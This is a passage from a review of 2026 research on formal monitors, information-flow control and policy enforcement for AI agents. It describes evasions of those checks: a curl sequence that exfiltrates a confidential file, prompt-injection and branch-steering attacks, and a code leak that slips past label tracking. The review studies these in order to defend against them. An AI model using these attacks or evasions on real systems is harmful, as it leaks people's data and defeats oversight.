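
The solver guarantees that the verdict follows from the answers and the formulas. If the language model answers "yes" to "Is this request for patient care?" about the nurse with the lecture, the solver correctly derives that the agent may open the record.

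Zhou and colleagues tested the system on the records of seven agent models, with Claude Opus 4.5 as the judge. Averaged over the seven, the accuracy was:

| Benchmark | Model judges directly | Model writes Python checks | FormalJudge |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Agent-SafetyBench (harmful actions) | 59.9% | 66.4% | 76.2% |
| VitaBench (users' constraints) | 66.2% | 69.8% | 74.8% |
| Deceivers (faked results) | 65.4% | 74.7% | 93.7% |

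"Accuracy" here means agreement with a majority vote of three leading models, one of which was Claude Opus 4.5 itself. So the large gains show that FormalJudge comes closer to the conclusions those models reach with more effort. If all three misunderstand a kind of case, the table won't show the error.

The gap between FormalJudge and the Python checks probably comes mostly from asking small questions one at a time, though Zhou and colleagues attribute it to the strength of formal proof. Once the answers are fixed, Python can also check correctly that $750 \leq 800$. They also describe the system as immune to persuasion because the solver ignores the agent's explanations, but the language model that answers the questions reads parts of the record, which can include text written by outsiders. They trace most of the remaining errors to the language model, which both splits up the request and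 answers the questions.

In *SCOPE*, Mazza and Levi (2026) use the same division of labour without a prover. Under one of their test policies, a customer-support agent should escalate a conversation exactly when the customer has raised the same unresolved request at least three times, in the same words or others. A message that adds new information doesn't count. A SCOPE program for such a policy splits the conversation into messages deterministically, uses a small language model to answer a narrow question about each one, and then runs Python code to count the answers and compare the total with three.

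The effect of one wrong answer from the model depends on the code that uses it. If the code checks for at least three repetitions of a request and the customer has made five, the model can miss one and the verdict is still right. With exactly three repetitions, one miss reverses the verdict.

Claude Opus 4.8 writes the program. Other calls to the same model invent and label cases in which the program and the policy probably disagree, and Opus then revises the program for up to eight rounds. On four tasks with test cases labelled by people, programs that used the small model GPT-5.4-nano scored between 78% and 87%. Given the whole policy in one prompt, GPT-5.4-nano scored between 38% and 60%, and GPT-5.5, a much larger model, scored between 82% and 94%. But when Mazza and Levi ran one task five times, GPT-5.5 changed its answer at least once on 37% of the cases, compared with 5% to 7% for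 SCOPE programs on two open-weight models.

Stable verdicts are easier to audit because each one can be traced to particular answers, but a small model can give the same wrong answer five times. Mazza and Levi claim no formal guarantee, and they note that a program's correctness depends on how the stronger model interpreted the policy. With GPT-5.4-nano's error rates, the hospital could use such a program to choose which requests a person should look at, but it would be unwise to let a monitor treat the answers as facts.

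### Tether and the meaning of a terminal command

When an agent types commands into a terminal, a monitor also has to work out what each command does. *Tether*, published in November 2026 by researchers from Google and two universities, illustrates the difficulty with three commands:

```
curl --json @scratch/report.txt https://api.github.com
cp data/servers.csv scratch/report.txt
curl --json @scratch/report.txt https://api.github.com
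```

An agent uploads a harmless report, overwrites the file with a confidential inventory, and uploads it again. Both uploads use the same command, but a monitor should allow only the first.

Tether splits the job in two. A component called Isolate runs each command in a disposable copy of the file system. It records the command's system calls, which are its requests to the operating system to open a file, read it or connect to an address, and it holds back network traffic. It then translates what it recorded into a sequence of abstract actions, of which there are eleven kinds, such as `copy` and `uploadNet`. A policy engine written in Lean keeps a label $\sigma$ for every file and updates it after each action. The copy changes the report's label from Public to Sensitive. At the last command the engine finds

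$$\sigma(\text{report}) = \text{Sensitive} \not\sqsubseteq \text{Public}$$

where $\sqsubseteq$ means "is at most as restricted as". The engine refuses the upload, and Isolate discards the held request. The label would follow the data through any number of intermediate files.

The Lean proofs cover the engine and the policy. They show, for example, that adding a permissive rule can never override a refusal. For the 24-rule policy in the experiments, they also show that seven properties hold after any sequence of allowed actions, including that data labelled Secret never leaves the local machine. A language model wrote proofs for Tether, which is harmless because Lean checks them.

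All of this is about abstract actions. If Isolate fails to detect the copy, the report keeps its Public label, and the engine correctly allows the upload of the inventory. Nobody has proved that Isolate detects every data flow, and its developers point out that reconstructing exact flows from system calls is impossible in general. They therefore design it to overestimate them. If a script reads one file and later writes another, Isolate treats the second as containing data from the first.

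Isolate was tested in two ways. In the first, a program generated workflows for which the right abstract actions were known in advance. It carried out each step by a randomly chosen method (a plain copy, a chain of several programs, or a transfer inside the kernel) and compared the engine's decisions with those actions. In the second, Gemini 3.8 Flash tried to steal or alter protected files in ten tasks. It succeeded 40% of the time against an early version of Isolate and never against the third version. One gap in the earlier versions involved hard links, which give a file a second name.

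In recorded runs from two benchmarks of coding agents, Tether blocked all 344 attacks and wrongly blocked 4.7% of 1,590 harmless runs. Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model reviews each command, caught 91.6% of the same attacks and had a 9.7% false alarm rate. But the 344 attacks include only those in which Isolate could trace and interpret every action, which excludes any that involve background processes or database queries. The developers also revised the policy after running it on benchmark recordings, so it may fit these cases better than new ones. They report that 28.2% of the runs in one benchmark and 22.1% in the other could be judged only by reading their content, as when an agent puts malicious code into a file it is allowed to edit.

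Tether's overcaution caused some false alarms. When an agent searched the whole disk for a word, the search program opened every file, including secret ones. Tether treated the agent as if it had read them and blocked its later actions.

Tether can't interpret the airline's booking database, so it couldn't identify which booking a terminal command had changed. But it can refuse every connection to the database. An agent then has to cancel bookings through the booking tool, where the call has a name and a monitor can apply the rule.

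### Taking untrusted text out of the plan

A monitor blocks any harmful call its rules cover, even if a prompt injection hidden in an email or web page led the model to propose it. But the injected text may also change a fact that the model supplies to the monitor. If a line in a forwarded letter gets the model to record "illness", the monitor will allow the cancellation.

Developers can train models to ignore such text or use filters to remove it, but both methods rely on learned behaviour and can fail. CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind, instead limits where the text can go. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe how it works. A privileged language model reads only the user's request and writes a plan as a short Python program. A quarantined language model reads the untrusted material, but it has no tools and can only return values. An interpreter runs the plan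 and labels every value with its sources and with who may read it. This is a simple plan:

```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant(
    f"Extract Bob's email from: {messages}", EmailAddress)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

An attacker who posts in the channel can't add another line to this program, because the channel's messages never reach the model that wrote it. But the attacker may get the quarantined model to return a different address. `email` is labeled as coming from the channel, and a policy can forbid sending messages to addresses from there.

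Nikolaou and colleagues turn these labels into formal predicates. Their rule for this case is

$$\mathsf{G}(\text{send} \rightarrow \text{recipient\_trusted})$$

and a model checker tests the plan against it before any tool runs. The plan above fails. No learned model has to judge whether the address looks suspicious, since a program computes the predicate from the plan.

This improves grounding, but the predicate only describes where the address came from. If Bob posts his own address in the channel, it gets the same label as an attacker's, so the harmless plan fails too.

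CaMeL also treats the user's request as trusted. That suits an assistant that works for one person, but the airline's agent takes requests from customers, who may want what the policy forbids. The airline could let the planner read only the airline's instructions and treat everything from the customer as data, but then it would have to foresee every kind of request.

### What the separation guarantees

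*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls CaMeL's main property "control-flow integrity". Trusted inputs determine the plan, and the agent can only follow paths in that plan. Untrusted data may select one of those paths but cannot add a new one.

The argument for this is convincing, but CaMeL has no machine-checked theorem behind it, and its tracking of labels has gaps. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, give an example, which in outline is:

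```
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("someone@example.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL would stop a plan that made the email directly conditional on the balance. Here, if the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and CaMeL marks it as secret. The line that changes `rich` doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is low, no email goes out, so the recipient learns whether the balance is high or low. An attacker can't write these lines into a CaMeL plan, so the practical risk may be small, but a general proof has to cover them.

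Garby and colleagues built a small programming language for agents in which such leaks cannot occur, and proved this in Lean. Roughly, the theorem is that if two runs differ only in their secret data, everything a public observer sees has the same probability in both, leaving aside whether the runs finish. A corresponding theorem holds for untrusted data and trusted results. The proof covers every program in the language, including programs that a language model writes during the run, and the verified interpreter is the one that calls the model. The guarantee depends on developers labeling data sources correctly.

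If no untrusted data may influence a payment, some useful tasks become impossible, such as "Pay the bill in this file." The language therefore has an explicit command, `endorse`, that lets a plan mark an untrusted value as acceptable. In 1,296 attacked runs on simulated banking tasks, the agent resisted all but two attacks. In both, the attacker had replaced the contents of the file with a fraudulent payment request, and the plan had endorsed whatever the file contained. Without `endorse`, the system blocks both this attack and payment of the genuine bill.

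Control-flow integrity can also fail when several agents work together, even if each one follows its own plan. Peters-Gill and colleagues asked a system of three CaMeL agents to send a colleague a summary of job applicants. A database record contained an injected instruction, which ended up in the summary. The coordinating agent never showed the instruction to its own planner, but it included the summary in its request to the agent that sends messages. That agent treated the request as coming from its user, so its planner read the injected instruction, and the agent also emailed the applicants' data to an outsider. The researchers' remedy is to pass instructions and data between agents through separate channels, and to have the interpreter reject any instruction that contains tool output.

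### The price in finished tasks

A planner that can't see the data has to anticipate what it will contain. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that most of the tasks lost under CaMeL are ones where an agent would normally take an extra step in response to a tool's output. On 112 industrial maintenance tasks, putting every agent under CaMeL lowered task success by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Separating the channels between agents lowered success by another 0.85 points for those two.

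They measured security on a different benchmark, with 949 attacks per model:

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | With separate channels |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% | 0% |

The figures are the shares of attacks that succeeded. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without an added defense, so on this test CaMeL would have reduced the number of tasks it finished without making it any safer. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against concluding that GPT-5.5 is immune, because attackers who adapt to their target have had some success against every leading model in a large public competition. For such a model, the benefit of CaMeL is protection against attacks that nobody has tried yet.

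These tests used CaMeL without any policies on data, such as the ban on untrusted recipients. When Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL with GPT-5.2 on 16 banking tasks, three times each, it finished 66.7% of the runs with policies off and 37.5% with them on. Their own agent finished 75% with its tracking always on, partly because of `endorse`. With so few tasks the margins of error are wide, but another group also found a large drop of this kind on messaging tasks.

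### When the condition is about the untrusted data

None of this establishes the customer's reason for cancelling. The airline agent's plan could be to read the message, have the quarantined model decide whether the insurance covers the reason, and cancel only if it does. The customer's text can't change the plan, but it determines which branch the agent takes. Researchers call an attack on this choice "branch steering", and control-flow integrity doesn't prevent it. Hiding the text from the quarantined model wouldn't help, because the decision depends on what the text says.

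Robots have the same problem with their sensors. Suppose a farm robot must never enter a row while a person is in it:

$$\mathsf{G}(\text{enter} \rightarrow \neg\,\text{person})$$

A learned detector sets the value of $\text{person}$ from the camera image. If somebody is crouching behind the leaves and the detector misses them, the monitor lets the robot into the row and records no violation. Using ten images instead of one may not help much, because leaves that hide a person in the first image probably hide them in the other nine. A bumper that stops the robot on contact needs no detector, but it acts only after the robot has touched the person.

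Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, tested agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. A planner wrote the whole program in advance, with a branch for each situation it could predict. At each branch, one learned model described the screen and another decided whether a condition held, such as "a cookie banner is visible". This design kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models. Foerster and colleagues then attacked it with an advertisement that looked like a cookie banner. Because the plan included a step for closing such banners, the agent could click on the advertisement and land on the attacker's site without departing from its plan.

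They considered two defences: comparing the screenshot with the page's underlying code, and asking a second model to confirm the first model's answer. They also built an attack against each. A fake banner with convincing code can get past the comparison, and small changes to the pixels can make the first model give an answer plausible enough for the second to accept. They conclude that any defence of this part will be probabilistic, because a click, unlike a bank transfer, has no fixed meaning that a policy could refer to.

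*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026) describes COBRA, a system that hands some of these decisions to a person. If its planner finds that only an untrusted observation could establish a condition, it asks the user before committing to the plan. This works when the user is the one who might be harmed. At the airline, the user is the customer whose word is in doubt, so the system would have to ask an employee instead.

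## How many rules are enforced, and whether the work still gets done

A checker can only guarantee compliance with rules that someone has formalized. If an airline faithfully formalizes half of its policy and gives the monitor accurate facts, the monitor can record no violations while the agent breaks rules in the other half. Developers therefore need to know how much of a real policy a program can enforce, and whether the agent still finishes its work when the program blocks calls.

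### How much of a policy a program can check

In *Don't Make Models Guess Security and Safety*, Hong, She and colleagues (2026) reviewed 80 agent safety and security benchmarks to find policies to study. In 61% of them, the designers never told the agent what counts as safe, and in another 24% they gave it only a vague goal, such as refusing anything "unsafe". Only seven benchmarks stated rules precise enough to check. Hong and colleagues analysed two of these, the airline tasks from *τ²-Bench* and a benchmark for in-car voice assistants. They also wrote a policy for MedAgentBench, in which an agent works with electronic medical records.

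| Policy | Statements | Of these, requirements on the agent | Of these, enforceable by a program |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Airline | 120 | 51 | 42 (82%) |
| Car assistant | 18 | 18 | 17 (94%) |
| Medical records | 88 | 57 | 34 (60%) |

Together that makes 93 of 126 requirements, or 74%. For 88 of the 93, a simple check is enough, such as confirming that a ticket belongs to the customer before cancelling it. The other five, all medical, need temporal logic or information-flow tracking.

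The airline's flown-status rule needs neither if the cancellation tool itself looks up the flights and rejects the request when the customer has flown any of them. Then nobody has to write a formula about the order of calls. Hong and colleagues were surprised that the benchmarks' tools leave out such basic checks.

The requirements that a program can't enforce concern tone, invented information, the order of a conversation, or judgement. For example, the airline's agent may not offer compensation unless the customer explicitly asks for it, and somebody has to decide what counts as asking. Hong and colleagues suggest that a developer could instead block the compensation tool until the customer's message is exactly the word "compensation". A program can check this different rule, but most customers with a genuine claim would never send that exact message.

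The 74% figure comes from the researchers' own classification and weights every rule equally. A hospital might care more about one of the unenforceable rules than about ten of the others.

### The 23 rules behind a violation rate of zero

The rules in the medical policy came from language models, not a hospital. GPT-5.2 drafted 50 rules from a description of the agent and its tools. An automated hazard analysis with GPT-5 produced 5,138 further candidates, which Hong and colleagues sampled, merged and split to get 38. Of the 34 rules they judged enforceable, they coded 23. The benchmark already enforced one, and the other ten needed medical knowledge they didn't have, such as the right dosage units for each drug.

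Without the added checks, GPT-5 broke at least one of the 23 rules in 23% of 300 ordinary tasks and in 62% of 50 tasks in which the user tried to manipulate it. With the checks, the violation rate was 0%. Like Soteria's 100% conformance, this figure follows from how the system is built. The 23 rules make up 40% of the 57 requirements on the agent.

Some of these checks also rely on information supplied by the model. In the airline tasks, the model must give the protected version of the cancellation tool the customer's identifier as an extra argument, which the tool compares with the identifier of the ticket's owner. If the model has already looked up the booking, it might copy the owner's identifier from there, and the check would then pass for any customer.

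### A generated policy that blocks almost every write

Coding rules by hand is slow, so Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026), in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, had Gemini 3 Pro translate the same 88-rule policy into Cedar. Their system borrows the hard and soft critics of LLM-Modulo. The hard critic, Cedar's own software, looks for the same kinds of error as AgentCore's automatic checks and returns any it finds to Gemini 3 Pro, which gets up to three new attempts. The soft critic uses two calls to Gemini 2.5 Flash to judge whether the rules match the English.

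Claude Opus 4.7 also transcribed constraints that appear in Hong and colleagues' program code but not in the policy text. Of the 29 rules that blocked at least one call, 15 came from the policy text and 14 from the code.

Mondl and colleagues tested the policy by replaying recorded runs from the earlier study. They report how many runs Cedar blocked, both in total and among runs with an attempted write to the records. The last column below is the difference between these two counts.

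| Tasks | Tools in the recorded run | Runs with a write: blocked | Runs without a write: blocked |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Ordinary | Plain web requests | 89 of 89 | 2 of 211 |
| Ordinary | Eight specific tools | 79 of 84 | 94 of 216 |
| Ordinary | The same, with the 23 coded rules | 85 of 86 | 82 of 214 |
| Manipulative | Plain web requests | 34 of 34 | 2 of 16 |
| Manipulative | Eight specific tools | 33 of 33 | 8 of 17 |
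| Manipulative | The same, with the 23 coded rules | 32 of 32 | 10 of 17 |

The policy blocked 94% to 100% of the runs that attempted a write. Mondl and colleagues take this as evidence that the policy covers more of the 88 rules than the hand-written code does. They are probably right, since it blocked many runs that had already passed the 23 coded rules. But a policy with the single rule "forbid every write" would have blocked 100% of these runs in all six rows.

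The policy blocked almost every write in the ordinary tasks, even though these tasks contain no attempts to provoke a violation. Two rules fired most often, 416 times each. One requires the agent to restate the patient's identity before a write, and the other requires confirmation. The equal counts suggest that both rules fired on the same calls, perhaps on every write. The agents may have skipped these steps, or they may have taken them in conversation, in a form that never reached the Cedar engine, which has no memory of its own.

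A recorded agent can't react to a block, so the replay can't show how many tasks would still have succeeded. In a live run, the agent might have asked for the confirmation and then completed the write. If every block had instead ended the task, at most 133 of the 300 ordinary tasks in the third row (44%) could have succeeded, whereas Hong and colleagues measured 67% with only their own rules in force. Mondl and colleagues say they evaluated coverage, not usefulness, and warn that developers switch off protections that get in the way too often.

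Even the coverage has gaps. With plain web requests, Hong and colleagues counted violations in 39% of the ordinary runs, while Cedar blocked only 30%. At least 26 runs that the hand-written checks flagged therefore passed the generated policy. (Some of the 26 may be runs that Hong and colleagues counted as unsafe because the agent couldn't supply an argument for the check.)

### The verifier tax

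In *The Verifier Tax*, Sah, Sah and colleagues (2026) ran agents live with a verifier in the loop, on 50 airline and 115 retail tasks from τ-bench, the predecessor of *τ²-Bench*. They tested two small open models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B. Each task ran three times in each of three set-ups: the model alone, the model with a verifier that applies general criteria, and the model with a verifier that also has the policy rules. The verifier is the same language model with a different prompt, so it isn't logically sound. After three rejections in a row, the software lets the last proposal through.

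To combine safety and usefulness in one number, Sah and colleagues define the safe success rate. With $s_i = 1$ if run $i$ finished its task correctly and $v_i = 1$ if it broke at least one rule, both being 0 otherwise, the rate over $n$ runs is

$$\text{SSR} = \frac{1}{n}\sum_{i=1}^{n} s_i\,(1 - v_i)$$

An agent that does nothing scores zero, and so does one that finishes every task by breaking a rule.

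The verifier intercepted up to 94% of the non-compliant actions, yet safe success stayed below 5% in most settings:

| Model and tasks | Success, model alone | Success, with policy verifier | Safe success, model alone | Safe success, with policy verifier |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 23.3% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% | 21.5% | 0.0% | 0.6% |
| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 25.3% | 0.7% | 4.7% |
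| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% | 5.5% | 2.6% | 2.9% |

In the study by Sah and colleagues, safe success was already between 0% and 2.6% with no verifier, and neither version of the verifier lowered it in any setting. The table therefore doesn't support the claim, often attributed to this study, that blocking unsafe actions stops agents from finishing their work. The verifiers did increase computation, with agents using 2.0 to 2.8 times as many tokens.

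Safe success was so low mainly because the models invented identifiers. In one retail task, a customer wanted to change a delivery address but was reluctant to give personal details. GPT-OSS-20B, running without a verifier, searched for a customer named John Doe with the postcode 12345. The tool accepted these details, the agent changed the order, and the benchmark gave the run full marks. Sah and colleagues found violations of this general kind in 93.7% of GPT-OSS-20B's retail runs.

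The verifier could hardly have helped, because its prompt required it to approve every search for a customer's identity. The 94% presumably excludes these searches. A symbolic monitor could reject any name or number that appears neither in the customer's messages nor in an earlier tool result, and Sah and colleagues propose something similar. However, they may count too many violations, because their definition includes identifiers "not grounded in retrieved environment state". If their auditing script applies that definition literally, it counts even a correct name and postcode that the customer typed as a violation. That could help explain why none of GPT-OSS-20B's successes without a verifier counted as safe.

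The recovery figures also look worse than they are. Sah and colleagues report that GPT-OSS-20B succeeded in 21% of the airline runs with an intervention, and that recovery in retail was near 0%. But the zero for this model's retail runs under the policy verifier is based on three cases. These agents mostly failed whether or not anything blocked them. Across all runs with a verifier, 18.7% of those with a rejection and no other error succeeded, compared with 21.3% of those with neither a rejection nor another error.

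In one successful recovery, a customer with a basic economy ticket asked for a full refund, claiming to have booked ten hours earlier. The database showed that the booking was more than 24 hours old and had no insurance. The agent started to process the refund anyway, and the verifier rejected it. The agent then explained the policy, held to it when the customer insisted, and passed the case to a human colleague, for which it received full marks.

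### Agents that finish as much work, or more

Several studies with symbolic checkers and better models found little or no loss in task completion. *Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) added four small programs, called gates, to the *τ²-Bench* airline tasks. One gate checks whether the policy allows a cancellation. *LEANGUARD* (Sankar, Ganguly and colleagues, 2026) used 45 rules written in Lean for the airline, retail and telecom tasks and proved that its monitor applies them correctly. A language model drafted the rules, and people corrected them. The paper also tested the monitor on DTap, a benchmark of attacks on agents, with a policy that allowed no writes.

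The table gives plain task success, and for Sankar and colleagues the version of the monitor that explains its refusals:

| Study | Agent and tasks | Without checker | With checker |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Hong and colleagues | GPT-4o, airline | 36% | 48% |
| Hong and colleagues | GPT-5, airline | 68% | 70% |
| Hong and colleagues | GPT-5, car assistant | 59% | 72% |
| Hong and colleagues | GPT-5, medical records | 59% | 67% |
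| Reddy and colleagues | GPT-4o mini, airline | 29.6% | 42.0% |
| Reddy and colleagues | GPT-5.2, airline | 61.2% | 71.6% |
| Sankar and colleagues | Five Qwen models, customer service | 72.7% | 70.9% |
| Sankar and colleagues | Five Qwen models, DTap without writes | 53.1% | 12.5% |

Chance could explain the two airline gains that Hong and colleagues reported, and also the 1.8-point loss in customer service. The gain for GPT-4o mini is well supported, because Reddy and colleagues repeated the experiment with 15 new runs per task and found almost the same difference. They did not repeat the test with GPT-5.2.

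When a monitor blocks every violation of its formal rules, the safe success rate under those rules equals the task success rate. GPT-5 with the airline checks therefore had a safe success rate of 70% on the 42 enforceable requirements. That is far above the figures for the two small models, but it leaves out the nine requirements that a program can't check. Sankar and colleagues tried to cover those with a language-model judge, which checked each run against the full English policy. It flagged 9.7% of the runs without a monitor and 6.5% of those with one. Some of the remaining flags were the judge's mistakes, and others concerned rules that nobody had formalized.

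### What decides the cost of a block

Blocking can raise the success rate because the benchmark scores a run by comparing the final state of the database with the correct one. A forbidden cancellation makes the task fail, but if the gate stops it and the agent then does nothing more, the database may be correct. In one task, a customer gives false information to get a cancellation. The agents with gates succeeded in all 16 attempts, and those without succeeded at most once in 16.

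The retail tools already reject most forbidden calls, so the gates added nothing there. Success fell from 62.5% to 57.8% on eight tasks, a difference that chance could explain. In the customer-service tasks of Sankar and colleagues, agents without a monitor made forbidden calls that changed data in only 28 of 1,390 runs, so blocking those calls couldn't have raised success by much.

Bad rules do more harm than bad agents. Reddy and colleagues compared each blocked call with the benchmark's correct solution. The cancellation gate was right all 161 times it blocked a call, but the baggage gate was right only 2 times out of 42, so it mostly stopped agents from doing their job. On DTap, the ban on writes cut successful direct attacks from 57.9% to 5.9%, but it also made every task that needs a write impossible. In the telecom part, where ordinary tasks rarely need a write, the success rate on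 those tasks hardly changed. A hospital that enforced Mondl and colleagues' policy without a way to give confirmations might also end up with an agent that can't complete tasks that need a write.

The model's ability matters because the agent has to find another way to complete the task after a block. In one airline task, GPT-4o mini kept running into the same gate and failed all five attempts. The best newer evidence on whether stronger models behave more carefully comes from Lin, Cao and colleagues (2026). *From Evidence to Action* tested Claude Opus 5, GPT-5.6 Sol and three other models, without guardrails, on 656 cases. In most cases, a run counts only if the agent establishes all the required facts before it acts. Before issuing a refund, for example, it must confirm that the charge is a duplicate.

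Overall success ranged from 38% to 67%. Although this measure differs from safe success on τ-bench, the results suggest that figures below 5% are specific to small models and one audit. They also show that the problem remains. Claude Opus 5 judged 98% of proposed actions correctly when Lin and colleagues asked it whether to allow them, but it handled only 60% of the single-action tasks correctly when it had to investigate and act itself. Its successors may do better. Lin and colleagues blocked no actions, so their results don't show how well such models recover from a block.

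Explaining to the agent why a call was refused also seems to help, but only modestly. Hong and colleagues attribute their gains partly to error messages that identify the rule a call broke. In a direct test by Sankar and colleagues, agents later completed 5.5% of the blocked actions in a permitted way after a bare refusal, and 9.1% after an explanation. Task success rose from 68.9% to 70.9%, which could be chance. The largest model improved most, from 3 recovered actions to 10 out of just under 60. The low recovery rates are partly appropriate, because the agents should never have made many of the blocked calls.

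Stronger models may need less guidance. In *AgentFaultBench*, Gupta (2026) gave agents guidance after tool errors, which differ from policy refusals. Revised guidance helped GPT-4o mini, while the stronger models already completed every case where recovery was possible.

A program can sometimes supply the correction itself. Sankar and colleagues had Lean search for a small change to a blocked call, together with a proof that the rules allow the changed call. Lean found one for 88 of the 252 calls blocked because of their arguments, typically in two milliseconds. Most of these corrections redirected a refund to the original payment method. Another 1,361 calls were blocked for reasons that changing the arguments couldn't fix, such as a missing approval or a skipped step. They ran the search only after the experiment, so no agent received a correction.

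Dantas and colleagues report that Agent-C, the system by Kamath and colleagues, already corrects calls while the agent runs. It restricts the text the model can generate so that a permitted call replaces a forbidden one. GPT-5's conformance rose from 83.7% to 100%, and its task score rose from 66.1% to 70.6%.

### How a systematic review grades the evidence

Dantas and colleagues rated the evidence for the field's nine main claims with GRADE, a scheme used in medical research. Each claim starts at "High" and loses one level each for weak methods, conflicting results, a narrow setting, and too little data. Seven of the nine claims ended at the lowest level, "Very Low", which means the true figure is likely to differ substantially from the reported one.

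The other two findings received a "Moderate" rating. One is that no agent scored above 60% on a large safety benchmark, and the other is that language models write temporal logic with valid syntax more than 90% of the time. Dantas and colleagues add that GRADE would normally start studies of this kind at "Low", and they suggest reading every rating one level lower under that stricter convention.

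The verifier tax, one of the seven, lost three levels because it rests on one study, covers only τ-bench, and lacks confidence intervals for its main figures. The review words the claim as "Enforcement reduces SSR", but safe success never fell in the original results. The review also describes the agents as inventing identifiers after a monitor had blocked the legitimate route, but the John Doe search happened in a run with no monitor.

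Another of the seven is that runtime enforcement achieves 100% conformance in closed domains. If a sound monitor sees every call, more trials wouldn't make that figure more certain. Researchers still need trials to find out whether the rules cover what matters in a new domain and how much work the agent completes under them.

Dantas and colleagues disclose weaknesses in their review. One person selected the studies. When three of the researchers repeated the search in September 2026, they found only 13 of the 38 studies, along with 11 others that all three would have included.

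Still, the low grades look justified. One of the seven claims, that language models translate few planning problems into PDDL correctly, rests on the 2024 Planetarium results, which the newest models have far surpassed.

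## Cheaper proofs and the proposal for guaranteed safe AI

The proofs described so far concern tool calls, such as whether the agent ran a status check before a cancellation. An airline cares about these calls because of their consequences, such as a passenger stranded overnight. In *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024) proposed proving claims about such outcomes, for AI systems in general and eventually for ones more capable than people. The 17 authors include the prominent AI researchers Yoshua Bengio and Stuart Russell. David Dalrymple was then at ARIA, a British research funding agency whose Safeguarded AI programme had the same aim.

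In 2024 the proposal had a practical weakness, because proofs about even simple programs took a lot of specialist work. Language models have since removed much of that work. This helps much more with some of the links that a guarantee depends on than with others.

### The argument for proofs

Testers can find failures, but they can't show that there are none. Dalrymple and colleagues recall that OpenAI evaluated ChatGPT for months, yet users got around its safety measures within a day of its release. A developer could also hide a backdoor that is cryptographically hard to detect without knowing the trigger, and a deceptive system might recognise a test and behave well only there. They compare AI with bridges. About a quarter of those built in the 1870s collapsed within the decade, and a deeper theory of engineering later brought the failure rate below 0.4% per decade. (Better materials and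 inspections presumably helped too.)

Even a long test supports only a modest claim. Dalrymple and colleagues conclude that a self-driving car that covers a million miles without needing intervention probably fails less than once per million miles. At the 95% confidence level used for the Ryanair policy, the bound is about three failures per million miles. These bounds hold only while conditions stay the same, and other drivers may become more aggressive once they are used to such cars.

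Zhang, Cai and colleagues (2025) make a related case for agents in *Trustworthy AI Agents Require the Integration of Large Language Models*, a position paper at ICML, a leading machine-learning conference. They conclude that a trustworthy agent needs both language models, which adapt well but produce plausible falsehoods, and formal methods, which are rigorous but hard to use. In their view, looking up documents gives a model better facts but does not make its reasoning more rigorous.

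In an example from the preprint of *Trustworthy AI Agents Require the Integration of Large Language Models*, GPT-4o turned an English description of a car's locks into a formal model that let the driver leave the key inside a locked car. A model checker found a sequence of steps that led to this result, and GPT-4o used that sequence to correct the model. The corrected model, which passed verification, lets the driver leave the key inside only while the door is open, and lock the door from outside only while holding the key.

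This is good evidence that formal tools find mistakes, but weaker evidence that agents require them. The result still depends on learned components, because in the system that Zhang and colleagues propose, a language model writes both the formal model and the assertions that the model checker tests. The formal model also leaves out things a real car might do, such as lock its doors by itself after a minute. Zhang and colleagues acknowledge that developers can't formalize every aspect of a system, particularly in unpredictable environments.

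### A world model, a specification and a verifier

Guaranteed safe AI has three components: a world model, a safety specification and a verifier. The world model describes mathematically how the AI's outputs affect the world. The specification states which effects are acceptable, and the verifier provides evidence that the AI meets the specification in that world model. For the airline, the specification might be "the agent strands at most one passenger in a million". The world model would then have to cover replacement flights, weather and what passengers do after a cancellation, none of which a monitor for tool calls has to model.

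The guarantee doesn't have to be a proof that harm never occurs. Dalrymple and colleagues also accept a sound upper bound on its probability, or an estimate of such a bound that converges as the verifier gets more computing time. They rank ways of building each component by how much safety each would provide if it worked:

| Component | Low on the scale | Higher | Top |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| World model (levels 0–5) | A trained simulator that nobody can inspect | Causal models that human experts have fully audited | None needed, because the specification covers all possible worlds |
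| Specification (0–7) | English that a black-box AI interprets | Parts written by AI, each audited by people | Everything people might want, in every context |
| Verifier (0–10) | Improvised tests | A sound bound on the probability of failure | The same, with a proof short enough for people to read |

FormalJudge corresponds to level 4 on the middle scale because its formula takes its inputs from a language model's answers. Soteria's rules are close to level 5 because a language model drafts them and people review them. The scale ranks how people produce a specification more than how much it covers, so a high level doesn't mean the rules include everything the airline cares about.

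Dalrymple and colleagues describe several ways to build world models. Engineers can write them by hand, as they do for aircraft controllers. A language model can write them as probabilistic programs, which people can read and audit. A learning system can also infer a distribution over many possible theories from data, so that its predictions remain uncertain where data are sparse. The most ambitious option is to prove that a model follows from the laws of physics, which would take an immense amount of computation.

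People are the hardest part to model. Dalrymple and colleagues doubt that a model of human behaviour can be both readable and highly accurate, and note that such a model would itself be a general AI. They suggest giving the verifier a set of possible behaviours instead of a prediction, and requiring the specification to hold for all of them. Soteria's verifier already does this for tools, since its proof covers every result that the tools' contracts allow. But if the airline's customers may write anything, nobody can prove that the agent never cancels because of a false excuse, unless it ignores excuses altogether.

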